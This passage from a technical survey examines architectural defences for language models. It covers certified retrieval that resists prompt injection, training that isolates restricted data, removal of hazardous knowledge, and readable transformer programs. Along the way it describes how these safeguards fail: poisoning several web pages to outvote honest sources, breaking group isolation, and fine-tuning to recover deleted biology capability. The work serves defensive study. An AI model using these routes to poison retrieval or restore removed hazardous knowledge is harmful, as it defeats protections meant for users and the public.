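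Certified accuracy is also much lower than accuracy against particular attacks. With another model, Mistral 7B, the keyword method answered 72% of the short RealtimeQA questions correctly under a prompt injection attack, but its certified accuracy was only 38%. Some of the uncertified questions may be safe for reasons the procedure can't prove, and some may fail against a better attack.

Larger groups give the model more context but leave fewer votes. With Mistral 7B and the token-by-token method, using one passage per group lowered accuracy by seven points when there was no attack. Groups of three removed this loss but lowered the certified share. RobustRAG took 1.16 to 3.65 times as long as ordinary RAG. It generates ten separate answers, but the time increases much less than tenfold because each run reads only one passage.

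### Later retrieval methods

*ReliabilityRAG* (Shen, Imana and colleagues, 2025) is designed to keep more of the information that keyword counting discards. It also gets a separate answer from each document, but uses a second model to detect contradictions between the answers. It selects the largest set of documents whose answers don't contradict each other, breaking ties in favor of higher-ranked documents, and gives the selected documents to the language model to read together.

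With GPT-4o-mini and no attack, this method scored 80.1 on biographies, compared with 61.2 for RobustRAG and 81.0 for ordinary RAG. It still scored 77.9 when the top-ranked document contained a prompt injection. These are test scores, and the method's guarantee is weaker than RobustRAG's. Shen and colleagues prove that the selected set is very likely to contain no malicious document if at most a fifth of the documents are malicious, the number of documents is large enough, and the contradiction detector rarely makes mistakes.

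The last condition is hard to meet. With nine honest documents, the theorem requires the detector to report false contradictions between honest answers less than 5.6% of the time, and the limit tightens as the number of honest documents grows. The detector that Shen and colleagues used is wrong on about 9% of cases in an ordinary benchmark and 30% in an adversarial one. These results give little reason to think that the condition holds, although the benchmarks don't measure exactly the kind of error that the theorem limits.

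*PRA-RAG* (Tan, Zheng and colleagues, 2026) forms many small subsets of the retrieved texts and represents each subset as a vector, rather than generating a separate answer for each passage. It then finds the smallest ball, centred on one of these vectors, that contains more than half of them, and gives the model a weighted average of the texts in the subset at the centre. This works only if most subsets contain no malicious text. Ten texts form 45 pairs, of which 28 are clean if two texts are malicious, but only 21 if three are.

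Tan and colleagues prove a limit on how far malicious texts can move the central vector. But the theorem doesn't limit how the model uses the vectors, so a small shift could still change the answer. When 20% of the retrieved texts in their tests were malicious, accuracy was 71% and the attack succeeded 1% of the time. Unlike RobustRAG's certified scores, these figures apply only to the attacks they tried.

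### What the certificates assume

Every certificate assumes a limit on how much the attacker controls, and the architecture can't enforce that limit. A certificate for a patch covering 2% of the image gives no protection against a larger one, and the main results for PatchGuard and PatchCURE allow only one patch. For documents, the number of pages is a poor measure of the attacker's effort. Someone who publishes the same false claim on six websites may control six of ten votes. Honest websites that copy the same mistaken press release have the same effect without any attack.

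RobustRAG's groups must also stay isolated when the system runs. A provider would probably process them in the same batch to save time, which could let a malicious passage affect other groups through shared rounding or expert-choice routing. The passage could then influence more than one vote, and the margin calculation would no longer hold. The Batch Isolation Checker could help confirm that the groups are isolated, if someone applied it to groups of passages rather than to users.

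Finally, enough of the separate pieces must contain the answer. Most photographs of a dog show recognisable parts of it in many places, and many web pages name the highest mountain. But a question that needs one fact from each of two documents may not be answerable from either one alone. Xiang and colleagues tested only questions that a single passage can answer, and suggest breaking harder ones into simpler questions first. Breaking up the question would not help with the emailed invoice, because the supplier's new account number may appear in only one message, with no other votes to compare it with.

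## Training experiments with separable modules and memories

The missing-path theorem and the certificates for votes both apply to a model whose weights are already set. Training data shapes those weights, and in an ordinary model every training text can change every weight a little. If a company trains such a model on files from a confidential project and later has to withdraw them, it cannot find the weights that hold their contents.

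Researchers have trained models in parts, so that a developer can delete or switch off the part that learned from particular data. If the data could not have affected any of the remaining weights, deleting that part leaves exactly the model that training without the data would have produced, given the same random choices. Otherwise, researchers can only find out by experiment how much information from the data reached the remaining weights.

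### One expert for each data domain

Under the definition that Tiwari and colleagues give, data a user may not access, such as another team's code, must never change that user's answers. Let $a$ be the user's permitted domains, write $D =_a D'$ when two datasets agree on all of them, and let $\mathcal M_D(a,x)$ be the distribution of answers to a query $x$ after training on $D$. The condition is then

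$$D =_a D'\;\Rightarrow\;\mathcal M_D(a,x)=\mathcal M_{D'}(a,x)\quad\text{for every }x.$$

The condition also covers the point at which the model stops writing, so a forbidden file can't even make an answer shorter.

Each domain's expert is an adapter, a small block of extra layers trained on top of a frozen public model. The system runs only permitted experts, but it still has to choose among them, and an ordinary learned router would let information from the other domains influence that choice.

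Suppose Ana is allowed to use projects A and B but not project C, whose files often mention a product called Falcon. A router trained on all three projects learns to send text about Falcon to C's expert and to give the other two experts lower scores, perhaps lowering A's more than B's. When Ana asks about Falcon, the system correctly skips C's expert, but C's files still affect her answer because training on them made the router choose B's expert over A's.

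Tiwari and colleagues replace the router with fixed rules. If the user names the domain a question belongs to, and may see that domain, the system looks up which permitted experts did best on held-out text from it. Otherwise a public text encoder turns the question and each permitted domain into vectors, and the system scores domain $n$ by

$$\phi_n+\lambda\,\frac{|d_n|}{\sum_{j\in a}|d_j|}.$$

Here $\phi_n$ is the similarity between the two vectors, $|d_n|$ is the number of training samples in the domain and $\lambda$ is a fixed weight. The second term favours experts with more training data. It sums only over permitted domains, because a sum over all domains would depend on the size of the forbidden ones. The three best experts then run in parallel, and the system averages their predictions, giving more weight to experts that have predicted the user's text well so far.

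A faster rule, meant for very large numbers of domains, seems to let forbidden domains influence the answer. It groups similar domains in advance and searches only the group nearest to the question. The system recomputes each group's centre from the permitted domains, but the grouping itself uses the vectors of all domains. A change in a forbidden domain could therefore move a permitted one into another group and change which experts the system uses. The slower rule avoids this and still takes only 0.16 seconds to search 10,000 domains.

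The experiments measured perplexity, which falls as a model gets better at predicting text. On posts from 50 Reddit forums, the modular version of GPT-2 had 38% lower perplexity than the version trained only on public data when the user could access every forum. Fine-tuning on all the forums without isolation lowered perplexity by 48%. When the user could access only one forum, the reduction averaged 11.5%. For OPT, another language model, tested on 79 code repositories, the reduction was 44% to 62% depending on the programming language, compared with about 75% without isolation. Even for users with full access, the modular models were less accurate than models trained without isolation, but they were far better than models trained only on public data.

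Delays grew by at most 1.9%, assuming each of the three experts runs on its own GPU. Running all three roughly triples the total computation. Merging their weights into a single model beforehand avoids this, but the Reddit gain then drops to 29%.

An auditor can't confirm the isolation from the finished weights, which don't record what data trained them, and would need the training code and logs. The guarantee also depends on the data's domain labels, not its content. If an employee pastes a confidential paragraph into a file that everyone may read, the model can repeat it without violating noninterference.

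### Experts trained by the data's owners

*FlexOlmo* (Shi, Bhagia and colleagues, 2025) lets organisations contribute to a shared model without handing over any data. The developer first trains a model with 7 billion parameters on public text. Each data owner takes a copy and adds a second expert to every layer, which starts as a copy of the public expert. The owner uses private text to train the new experts and the row of router weights that scores each one. Everything else stays frozen, so all the owners' experts learn to work beside the same public experts. The developer then merges the models by putting the experts side by side in each layer and stacking their router rows.

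When an owner opts out, the model's operator deletes the owner's expert and its row. No other weight received an update that depended on the owner's data, so the remaining model is the same as if the owner had never joined. The owner can verify much of this without trusting anyone, because no other participant ever held the data. The owner still has to trust the operator to delete the expert.

An optional last step weakens this guarantee. Each owner trains a classifier to find public documents that resemble its private ones, and the developer tunes all the router rows together on the documents the classifiers select. If the developer later deletes one owner's row, the other rows keep adjustments that depended on that owner's selected documents and expert. Removing an owner exactly therefore requires using the untuned router or repeating the tuning without that owner.

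The table compares versions with experts for mathematics, code and educational text. The average covers 24 tasks.

| Model | Average | Mathematics | Code |
|---|---|---|---|
| Public data only | 36.9 | 8.1 | 1.0 |
| FlexOlmo, untuned router | 46.7 | 51.5 | 18.2 |
| FlexOlmo, tuned router | 47.8 | 50.7 | 17.3 |
| Ordinary MoE, same computation, half the data | 46.3 | 49.4 | 22.2 |
| Ordinary MoE, all the data, twice the computation | 51.5 | 53.4 | 27.0 |

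Without the tuning step, the model scores about one point lower. The untuned model does about as well as an ordinary MoE trained on all the data sources together with the same amount of computation. It scores 4.8 points lower than an ordinary MoE trained with twice the computation, and the gap is largest on code.

Opting out can't undo leaks of training data that occurred while the expert was in use. Shi and colleagues took 10,000 documents from the mathematics data, gave each model the first 32 tokens of each document, and counted how often at least one of ten continuations nearly matched the original. The rate was 1.6% for a model trained only on that data after the public stage, 0.7% for FlexOlmo with the mathematics expert, and 0.1% for the public model, which was not trained on the documents. Shi and colleagues recommend that owners of sensitive data train their experts with differential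 privacy.

### Memory that can be edited

The simplest way to make data removable is to keep it out of the weights. A system that retrieves documents can check the user's permissions before it searches, so that forbidden documents never enter the model's input. Deleting a file then removes it from all future answers, as long as no cache or saved note holds a copy. The search needs the same care as a router, because a ranking that gives extra weight to words that are rare in the whole collection depends slightly on documents the user isn't allowed to see.

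Tiwari and colleagues argue that such a store can't replace training entirely. Retrieved text makes the input longer, so processing it takes more compute, and training seems better suited to teaching a model a new style or a field's terminology. Models also often need fine-tuning before they use retrieved text well. If the developer fine-tunes on the restricted documents, those documents influence the weights again.

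Fountzoulas (2026), in *Kathleen Remembers*, instead keeps a memory inside the model but makes it simple enough to edit by arithmetic. The memory is a single vector that the model adds to as it reads:

$$\text{mem}=\sum_t \beta_t\,(k_t\circledast v_t).$$

Here $v_t$ is a fixed random vector for the byte being stored, $k_t$ is a key computed from the bytes before it, and $\beta_t$ sets how strongly it is stored. Circular convolution, $\circledast$, combines two vectors so that the same key can later recover an approximate copy of $v_t$. Training never changes the keys, so anyone with the original text can recompute a fact's terms and subtract them, leaving the sum the memory would have held if the fact had never been written.

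With five facts in memory, the model recalled 82.5% of the bytes correctly. After one subtraction erased a fact, recall of that fact fell to 4.3% (chance is 3.8%), while recall of the other four was 84.1%. The result was similar on texts four times as long as those in training.

The subtraction is exact only for the memory vector. The rest of the model also read the fact and keeps a fading trace of it in a recurrent state. Fountzoulas found that this part alone recalled almost nothing, but that result does not prove that the fact can't be recovered from it. In a later version, each new entry slightly weakens the older ones, so erasing an entry exactly also requires restoring what it weakened. The model is small, with about 212,000 parameters, and it erases facts it read as input, not facts it learned from training data. A version that worked with whole words gained little from the memory.

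### Why deleting a module can leave traces

In Tiwari and colleagues' design and in FlexOlmo, the shared weights learn nothing from restricted data. This is a drawback when a model could also learn something general from that data. In *Memorization Sinks*, Ghosal, Maini and Raghunathan (2025) wanted a model to learn from texts repeated many times in its training data without being able to recite them.

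They first tried reserving some neurons for the repeated texts. Neurons here are the units in the part of each layer that processes each position separately. Repeated texts updated only the reserved neurons and all other texts updated only the rest, but both groups of neurons ran on every text. The model learned more slowly than an ordinary one, and deleting the reserved neurons made it worse on new text.

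A model with two weights shows why. Let its output be $g+m$, where $g$ is the general weight and $m$ the reserved one, and suppose the restricted data has set $m$ to 0.4. For a public example whose correct output is 1, training with step size $\eta$ updates the general weight by

$$g\leftarrow g+\eta\,(1-g-m).$$

The general weight $g$ settles at 0.6. Without the restricted data, $g$ would have settled at 1 and $m$ would have stayed at zero. Deleting $m$ therefore leaves the model with the wrong answer, 0.6 instead of 1, and anyone who knows the setup can work out what $m$ was. The restricted data never updated $g$, but it still influenced $g$ through the forward pass, the computation that produces the output. Ghosal and colleagues prove a similar result for a two-layer linear network, whose difference from a model that never saw the restricted example grows with further training.

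Their solution is to run each of the reserved neurons, called sinks, on only a few texts. Each training text has an identity number that selects a fixed subset of the sinks, while all texts update the general neurons. When the same text returns, its sinks still hold the exact wording, because few other texts have overwritten them. Training therefore does little to store the wording in the general neurons as well, and whatever they did store fades as they learn from other texts. After training, the developer deletes all the sinks.

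In models with 360 million and 1.7 billion parameters, deletion closed at least half of the gap in loss between repeated texts and similar unseen ones. A good deal of memorisation therefore survived, as expected when every text updates the general neurons. The models still did about as well on new text as ordinary models trained with the repetitions. The method still worked when up to 10% of repetitions had wrong identity numbers, but worked poorly at 50%. Ghosal and colleagues did not test it against deliberate attempts to extract the texts, which they leave to future work.

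### Choosing which weights a text may change

Cloud, Goldman-Wetzler and colleagues (2024), in *Gradient Routing*, introduced the general method behind most later work on removable capabilities. Training works backwards from the loss $L$ to find how each value in the network affected it. Gradient routing multiplies each step of this calculation by a mask chosen for the training example:

$$\frac{\tilde\partial L}{\tilde\partial v}=\sum_{u}\alpha_{vu}\,\frac{\tilde\partial L}{\tilde\partial u}\,\frac{\partial u}{\partial v}.$$

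The sum covers the values $u$ computed directly from $v$. Setting the mask $\alpha_{vu}$ to one gives ordinary training, and setting it to zero stops the example from changing anything further back along that connection. The mask does not affect the forward pass.

In one test, a network compressed images of handwritten digits into a code of 32 numbers and then reconstructed the images from it. Images of 0–4 could train only the first half of the code and images of 5–9 only the second half, while a penalty discouraged large values in the code. A separate decoder that saw only the second half could reconstruct 5–9 but produced nearly the same image for all of the digits 0–4.

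For language models, Cloud and colleagues add new neurons to some layers, steer updates from the unwanted texts towards those neurons during training, and then delete the neurons. A short round of fine-tuning on other data repairs the damage from the deletion. They also found that routing can catch related material that nobody labelled, an effect they call absorption. When they routed only the word "California" to one number in the residual stream, that number also became associated with Oregon, Texas and Sacramento.

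Shilov, Cloud and colleagues (2025), in *Beyond Data Filtering*, simplified the method into selective gradient masking. They reserve some neurons and attention heads in every layer for the unwanted subject and treat each kind of text differently. In their main test the subject was biology:

| Training text | Part of the model that runs | Weights the text changes |
|---|---|---|
| Labelled as biology | All of it | Biology weights only |
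| Labelled as not biology | All except the biology weights | General weights only |
| Unlabelled | All of it | All weights |

After training, the developer sets the biology weights to zero. Even perfect labels would not ensure noninterference, because the general weights learn from unlabelled text while the biology weights are active, as in the two-weight example. In the test, 90% of the articles on other subjects counted as unlabelled.

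Shilov and colleagues trained a model with 254 million parameters on English Wikipedia and compared it with models trained on filtered data, which left out the unwanted articles. At any given level of general performance, their model predicted biology text less well than a model trained without the biology articles, even when the filter also removed medicine, chemistry and environmental science. This is probably because articles on other subjects contain some biology, which a filter that works on whole articles can't remove. The method slowed general learning by 5–6%.

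### GRAM's deliberate leak

*Modular Pretraining Enables Access Control* (Roland, Cubuktepe and colleagues, 2026) extended the approach to several subjects at once. Its method, GRAM, adds a small module for each restricted subject to every layer, beside a large core that always runs. The developer can then serve each customer the same model with a different set of modules.

For a batch of virology text, the core and the virology module both run. Training always updates the module, and with probability $p_{as}$ it also updates the core and all the other shared weights. For a batch of general text, the core usually runs alone, but with probability $p_{cr}$ a randomly chosen module runs too, which teaches the core to work with or without modules.

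Both probabilities let restricted data affect the shared weights. When $p_{as}$ is above zero, virology text changes them directly. A nonzero $p_{cr}$ lets a module's contents influence what the shared weights learn from general text, so setting only $p_{as}$ to zero would not isolate them. Roland and colleagues accept the leak because a higher $p_{as}$ makes the model better at the restricted subjects. In their main test, $p_{as}$ was 0.5 and $p_{cr}$ was 0.2. They sampled 40 million tokens of virology text at three times its normal rate, so about 60 million tokens' worth of virology updates reached the shared weights. It therefore can't be proven that deleting the module removes the knowledge.

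Filtering, unlike GRAM, gives exact removal, but it needs a new model for every combination of subjects. Roland and colleagues therefore test how closely GRAM matches filtering. They express each result as a share of an ordinary model's training, so a score of 0.6 means the loss that model had reached after 60% of its training. The table gives results for a model with 26 million parameters trained on children's stories, with four of 48 topics restricted. "Retrained" means after brief fine-tuning on 128 stories from each removed topic.

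| Method | General text | Kept topics | Removed topics | Removed, retrained |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Filtering | 0.96 | 0.96 | 0.78 | 0.87 |
| GRAM | 0.94 | 0.95 | 0.77 | 0.86 |
| Adapters on a frozen model | 0.84 | 0.93 | 0.69 | 0.77 |
| Unlearning after ordinary training | 0.96 | 0.93 | 0.84 | 0.98 |

GRAM did slightly worse than filtering on general text as well as on the removed topics, and deleting a module can itself do some damage. Its lower score on the removed topics therefore doesn't mean that it removed more knowledge than filtering did.

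The larger experiments covered virology, cybersecurity, nuclear physics and the programming language Lisp. Roland and colleagues trained models of seven sizes, from 50 million to 5 billion parameters, and compared GRAM using only its virology module with a model whose training data was filtered to general text and virology. GRAM performed similarly to the filtered model at every size. On the removed subjects, both fell further behind an ordinary model as size increased. One GRAM training run supported five sets of capabilities with about a fifth of the computation needed to train five filtered models.

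The evidence is weaker for the largest models, with only one run each at 2 billion and 5 billion parameters. The largest GRAM model also scored unexpectedly high on virology. Roland and colleagues attribute this to an interaction with the model's settings and mark their guess at the correct value on the chart.

The adapters deserve more attention than this comparison gives them. They are added to a frozen model that was never trained on restricted data, so removing them restores that model exactly. They performed worse than GRAM on the stories but about as well on the four real subjects, including at larger sizes. In this setting, with correct labels and little restricted data, a developer could therefore get exact isolation with about the same amount of training. GRAM did better when several modules ran together. Its performance on virology stayed the same when the other three modules were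 on, whereas combining adapters usually made them perform worse.

### Moving knowledge out of a finished model

All these methods have to start before the model learns the restricted material. Jin, Ma and colleagues (2026), in *Towards Architectural-Level Safety Control*, try to separate hazardous knowledge in MoE models that have already finished their main training. Their method, REX, works in four steps:

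1. In each layer, find the eight experts that hazardous text uses most compared with general text. Copy them as new experts and weaken the originals.
2. Continue training. Hazardous text changes only the new experts, and general text changes only the old ones, which have to manage without the new experts. Both kinds of text train the router, with extra penalties that steer hazardous text towards the new experts.
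3. Delete the new experts.
4. Apply a standard unlearning method, RMU, which pushes the remaining model's internal vectors for hazardous text towards a random direction.

Attention and the other shared weights stay frozen in the second step, so anything hazardous they already contain remains after the deletion. The table shows scores on WMDP-Bio, a multiple-choice test of hazardous biology where guessing scores 25%. The last two rows show results for the fully cleaned model after 250 million tokens of ordinary fine-tuning.

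| Treatment | Qwen3.5 | Intern-S2 | Gemma 4 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Original model | 83.2 | 83.4 | 78.9 |
| New experts deleted | 62.9 | 64.3 | 70.2 |
| RMU alone, without new experts | 41.6 | 33.3 | 48.5 |
| New experts deleted, then RMU | 32.4 | 29.6 | 33.6 |
| Fine-tuned with the new experts, then deleted | 42.8 | 55.0 | 41.3 |
| Fine-tuned after deletion | 63.0 | 64.6 | 55.7 |

Deletion alone leaves most of the knowledge in place, and much of the final reduction comes from a method that changes weights without removing any. But the new experts do hold some of it. Putting them back into the cleaned Qwen3.5 model raised its score from 32.4% to 80.8%. In Intern-S2, the score was 64.3% after deleting the new experts and about 79% after deleting the same number of randomly chosen old ones.

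### How removed knowledge can survive or return

Exact isolation is vulnerable to missing labels. Filtering and adapters on a frozen model both treat unlabelled text as general, so an unlabelled virology paper trains the shared weights. When Roland and colleagues removed half of the labels, both methods scored 0.85 on the subjects they were meant to remove, while GRAM scored 0.60. GRAM runs and updates all its modules on unlabelled text, and the module already trained on a subject seems to absorb most of what the model learns from unlabelled text on that subject.

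Shilov and colleagues measured this effect in a model trained on English and Spanish stories, with Spanish as the unwanted subject. When a fifth of the Spanish text was unlabelled, the model saw 144 million unlabelled Spanish tokens. After deletion, it knew as much Spanish as an ordinary model would have learned from 965,000 tokens, about 0.7% as many. This percentage was higher in smaller models. Unlabelled text can update every part of the model, including the part that is later deleted, so these methods can remove knowledge learned from it. For the same reason, there is no proof that the remaining parts learned nothing unwanted. A developer with poor labels may still remove more unwanted knowledge this way than with exact isolation, which requires reliable labels.

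Even perfect isolation doesn't stop a model from working out things it was never taught. On the children's stories, filtered models reached 0.78 on topics they had never seen, because most of what helps predict a story is common to all stories. Larger models fell further behind on the removed subjects, possibly because more of what they learn is specific to a subject. But this trend was measured only up to 5 billion parameters, and Roland and colleagues don't claim that it continues to the largest systems. A user can also put the missing information into the prompt, and Shilov and colleagues expect their method to be as vulnerable to this as filtering.

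The overlap between subjects also means that removal weakens the model in related areas. After REX, scores on MMLU, a broad test of knowledge, fell by up to 5.6 points in the biology experiments. The ten biology and health subjects make up 15% of the questions but accounted for 57–75% of the decline. A model that can't help with dangerous biology may therefore also be less useful to a medical student.

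Fine-tuning is the harder test, since it can reveal knowledge that a method has only hidden. Filtering is the reference point, because a filtered model has no hidden knowledge to recover and must learn the subject from the new data. In the Wikipedia experiment, a model treated with RMU reached an ordinary model's performance on biology after 50 steps. The model trained with selective gradient masking took 350 steps, the same as the model trained with the strict filter, and the model trained with the filter that removed only biology articles took 325.

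Roland and colleagues gave an attacker 512 passages from each removed subject, about half a million tokens, and let the model train on them for up to 200 rounds. GRAM again resisted about as well as filtering. Larger models appeared to resist better, but they had also trained on more data, so the attacker's 512 passages were a smaller share of the total. With much more data or computation, an attacker would probably recover part of the capability even from a filtered model.

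REX held up less well when someone fine-tuned the public version directly. Scores on hazardous biology rose from about 30% to between 56% and 65%, although the fine-tuning data left out the life sciences. Scores were lower, at 41–55%, when the developer fine-tuned the complete model and then deleted the experts. People who download the public version can't do this because they don't have those experts, so any further training changes the weights that remain.

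## Models built to be read as programs

Some researchers have restricted networks so that a person can read what they compute, which neither separable modules nor a bound on opaque serial depth makes possible. *Learning Transformer Programs* (Friedman, Wettig and Chen, 2023) introduced a transformer that learns from data and can then be converted automatically into a Python program with the same behaviour. *Mechanisms of Symbol Processing for In-Context Learning in Transformer Networks* (Smolensky, Fernandez and colleagues, 2024) instead compiles hand-written programs into transformer weights, so the resulting networks are readable but learn nothing from data.

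### Named variables and matching rules

A Transformer Program gives each variable its own slot in the residual stream, whereas in an ordinary transformer one number in the stream may mix contributions from many components. At first the stream holds two variables at each position, the token and the position number. Each variable has $k$ possible values and occupies $k$ numbers, one of which is 1 while the rest are 0.

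An attention head has three gates, which select the variables it uses as query, key and value. Each gate $\pi$ contains a single one and otherwise zeros, so what the head reads through it is

$$\mathrm{read}(x)=\sum_{i=1}^{m}\pi_i x_i,$$

where $x_1,\dots,x_m$ are the variables in the stream. The head gets one variable whole and nothing from the others. Its output $h(x)$ becomes a new variable at the end of the stream,

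$$x'=[x;\,h(x)],$$

and no later module can overwrite it. The price is that the stream gets wider with every module.

A table in each head pairs every query value with one key value. The head finds the positions whose key matches and copies the value variable from the closest one. If nothing matches, it copies from the first position. Two such heads are enough to continue the sequence "a1b2b2a" with "1". The first stores the previous token at each position. The second finds a position where the stored token is "a" and copies the token at that position.

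Some attention heads count matching positions instead of copying a value from one of them. Each feed-forward layer acts as a lookup table that reads two variables and writes one. If each variable can take $k=8$ values, the conversion procedure can run the layer on all 64 combinations and list the results. Finally, a classifier adds up learned weights for the variables and returns the label with the highest total.

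Training by gradients can't adjust an all-or-nothing choice, so each choice starts out soft. If $\phi_i$ is the learned score of option $i$ and $\epsilon_i$ is random noise, the option gets the weight

$$\frac{\exp\left((\phi_i+\epsilon_i)/\tau\right)}{\sum_j\exp\left((\phi_j+\epsilon_j)/\tau\right)}.$$

Friedman and colleagues lowered the temperature $\tau$ from 3.0 to 0.01 during training. At the start, two options with scores of 2 and 1, including noise, get weights of 0.58 and 0.42. By the end, the option with the higher score gets practically all the weight. The conversion procedure then keeps only the best option for each choice.

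### Counting tokens

In the histogram task, the model must write under each token how often that token occurs, so "abbc" requires 1, 2, 2, 1. A single counting head can do this. Its query and key are both the token variable, its table pairs each letter with itself, and its value is a variable called "ones" that equals 1 everywhere. With rows for queries and columns for keys, the matches and their sums are

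$$\begin{pmatrix}1&0&0&0\\0&1&1&0\\0&1&1&0\\0&0&0&1\end{pmatrix}\begin{pmatrix}1\\1\\1\\1\end{pmatrix}=\begin{pmatrix}1\\2\\2\\1\end{pmatrix}.$$

In slightly simplified Python, the head becomes:

```python
partner = {"a": "a", "b": "b", "c": "c"}

def matches(query, key):
    return key == partner[query]

counts = [sum(matches(q, k) for k in tokens) for q in tokens]
```

The classifier still has to turn each count $n$ into a label. It can do this by giving label $c$ the score $2cn-c^2$, which equals $n^2-(n-c)^2$ and is therefore highest when $c=n$. For a count of 2, the labels 1, 2 and 3 get scores of 3, 4 and 3.

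### What an auditor can check

The architecture ensures that the code exists, whatever weights training produces. Training still sets the gates, so an auditor has to read the finished program to see which variables affect which. If no chain of gates leads from a variable to the output, the missing-path theorem applies to that program, but the auditor has to check again if someone retrains the model.

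The auditor must follow all three gates of each head. A key can affect the output even if the head never copies it, because it helps determine which position the head copies from. Denning pointed out this kind of flow in 1976. Named variables alone also do not separate trusted text from untrusted text. In the invoice case, the owner's words and the email's words would both be in the token variable, at different positions, and a head that reads this variable could copy from either. Blocking the email's influence would still require a mask, or a proof that the email can never change what a head copies or counts.

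An auditor can test every input if the inputs are short. A formal proof uses a solver, software that searches for values meeting a list of logical conditions. The auditor translates the program and the task into such conditions and has the solver search for an input of a given length on which the program gives a wrong answer. If none exists, the program is correct on every input of that length, provided the translation is accurate. The proof requires an exact definition of the right answer, which is easy to write for counting but hard for deciding which invoices to pay.

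### Good scores and wrong answers

Friedman and colleagues tested programs on seven small algorithmic tasks, with inputs of at most 16 tokens for the bracket tasks and eight for the others. Five of the programs got more than 99% of tokens right. They also trained a program to label names in news sentences, with a vocabulary of 10,000 words. Its F1 score, which accounts for both missed names and false alarms, was 76.1, compared with 70.5 for a standard transformer trained on the same data and 66.2 for a method that looks at each word alone. On four text-classification tests, the programs came within three points of standard transformers. Three of these tests are weak evidence because a method that ignores word order also came within about two points.

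In *What Accuracy Hides in Learned Transformer Programs*, Lee, Oozeer and Quirke (2026) measured how often the whole answer was right. They added two addition tasks and trained 2,160 models, using 48 configurations per task and five random starts per configuration. The table gives their best results as percentages, next to the original scores. "Improved" means the best result after they changed the training data or the model.

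| Task | Tokens, 2023 | Tokens, 2026 | Whole answers | Whole answers, improved | Error found in improved version |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Histogram | 100.0 | 100.0 | 100.0 | 100.0 | None up to 7 values |
| Sorting | 99.8 | 100.0 | 100.0 | 100.0 | None up to 6 values |
| Double histogram | 98.4 | 98.4 | 97.5 | 100.0 | None up to 7 values |
| Reversal | 99.8 | 100.0 | 99.8 | 99.8 | Yes |
| Brackets, one type | 99.3 | 99.9 | 98.6 | 98.6 | Yes |
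| Brackets, two types | 99.1 | 99.4 | 95.8 | 96.5 | Yes |
| Ranking by frequency | 75.7 | 82.9 | 16.5 | 57.6 | Yes |
| Addition | – | 75.1 | 2.7 | 76.3 | Yes |
| Addition with place hints | – | 91.5 | 39.7 | 84.2 | Yes |

The ranking result overstates what comparing the two columns can show, because the improved model's test had more ties and its score comes from the soft version.

A program with a perfect test score could still make errors. The original sorting program scored 100% but changed six 3s into one 1 and five 3s. The histogram program, given seven copies of "4", answered 6 at every position. Its code showed that it counted seven correctly, but the classifier had no label 7 because no training example had required that answer. The scoring rule in the example above would make the same error without a label 7, because 6 would then score highest for a count of seven.

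Lee and colleagues then ran another histogram model of the same size on all 335,922 possible inputs of up to seven values. It failed on 42, all with one value appearing six or seven times. They added training examples with large counts and retrained from five random starts, and all five models answered every input correctly. Sorting was harder to repair, and after about 30 exploratory retraining runs, only one of five runs with the chosen recipe passed the complete check.

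In the ranking task, the model must list the distinct values from most to least frequent. For the input 1, 3, 4, 3, 4, 4, 4, it returned 4, 4, 1 instead of 4, 3, 1. A head had correctly counted four 4s. Without that count, the classifier scored 3 slightly above 4 for second place, 15.894 to 15.797. The count lowered the score for 3 by 8.584 but the score for 4 by only 1.445, so the model chose 4. After retraining, the program returned 4, 1, 1, again because it used a correct count wrongly.

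Hardening a model's choices can also make it much less accurate. One addition model got 90.5% of whole answers right while its choices were still soft, but the Python program extracted from it at that point got 14.2%. An auditor therefore has to test the extracted program rather than rely on the soft model's scores.

### Networks with few connections

In *Weight-sparse transformers have interpretable circuits* (2025), Gao, Rajaram and colleagues at OpenAI kept ordinary transformer operations but removed most of the connections. They trained models on Python code and, after each training step, set all but the largest weights in every matrix to zero. They gradually reduced the number of weights kept, until about one in 1,000 remained in the sparsest models. Sparse attention is a different technique that skips positions in the text, usually to save time.

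To find out how a model performs a task, the researchers looked for a circuit, a small set of nodes that can do the task alone. A node is a single neuron or channel, and an edge is a nonzero weight between two nodes. They wrote 20 tasks, each with two possible continuations, such as closing a string with a single or double quotation mark. A pruning procedure learns an on-off switch for each node and freezes the switched-off nodes at their average values. The goal is the smallest circuit that reaches a loss of 0.15, which corresponds to a probability of about 86% for the right continuation.

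At the same overall prediction loss, circuits in the sparse models had about one-sixteenth as many edges as those in dense models, which keep nearly all their weights. Gao and colleagues also found that removing only the circuit severely damaged the network's performance on the task.

The quotation-mark circuit has 12 nodes and 9 edges. One neuron detects an opening quotation mark and another records its type. An attention head uses the detector to find the mark and copies its type to the end of the string.

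Another circuit determines whether to close a list with one bracket or two by averaging a signal for open brackets over the preceding text. Two open brackets average 0.2 over ten tokens but only 0.05 over 40, which suggests that the circuit may fail on long lists. As predicted, the complete model failed to close long nested lists correctly, and so did dense models of similar ability.

Sparse connections make a model easier to inspect, but sparsity alone does not rule out any particular path. The four main components of the quotation-mark circuit have 41 edges to the rest of the network, and the circuit uses only nine. The training procedure is also designed to leave every neuron at least four nonzero weights. If each node took input from four others and their paths never met, six steps back would reach $4^6=4{,}096$ nodes, twice the 2,048 channels in most of these models. Because the zeros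 are exact, an auditor can search the finished weights for paths. But training determines which weights stay nonzero, so another run could leave different paths open.

### Is the circuit what the model uses?

*Weight-sparse circuits may be interpretable yet unfaithful* (Drori, 2026) repeated the experiment on simple stories and mostly confirmed that sparse models have smaller circuits. But the pruning procedure also found circuits for things the model doesn't do. The circuit for choosing "he" or "she" to match a name had about ten nodes. The circuit for a nonsense version of the task, which required "is" after a male name and "when" after a female one, had only about 30 nodes and was more than 95% accurate.

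In another task, the model had to choose "him" or "her" to match the first of two names. Drori pruned the model using only sentences whose names had opposite genders. When both names had the same gender, the full model gave the right pronoun an average probability of 81%, while many of the pruned circuits gave it almost none. These circuits apparently chose the opposite of the second name's gender. Drori set removed nodes to zero, which gave smaller circuits than freezing the nodes at their averages but may have made the circuits less faithful to the full model. Drori criticizes the pruning and draws no conclusion about sparse training itself.

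A pruned circuit is a new network, so checking it does not establish how the deployed network behaves. For an auditor, this is a serious difference from Transformer Programs, whose code describes the entire model.

In *Individual Parameters in Weight-Sparse Transformers Appear Interpretable*, Marin-Llobet and Heimersheim (2026) examine individual weights rather than circuits. They delete a weight, find where the model's predictions change, have a language model write a short rule describing those places, and test the rule on new text. Rules held up for 15% of the sampled nonzero weights in OpenAI's model and 9.6% in Drori's sparse model, compared with 1.5% and 0.4% in two dense models. Each rule describes when a weight matters but not what it computes.

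### Readability at larger sizes

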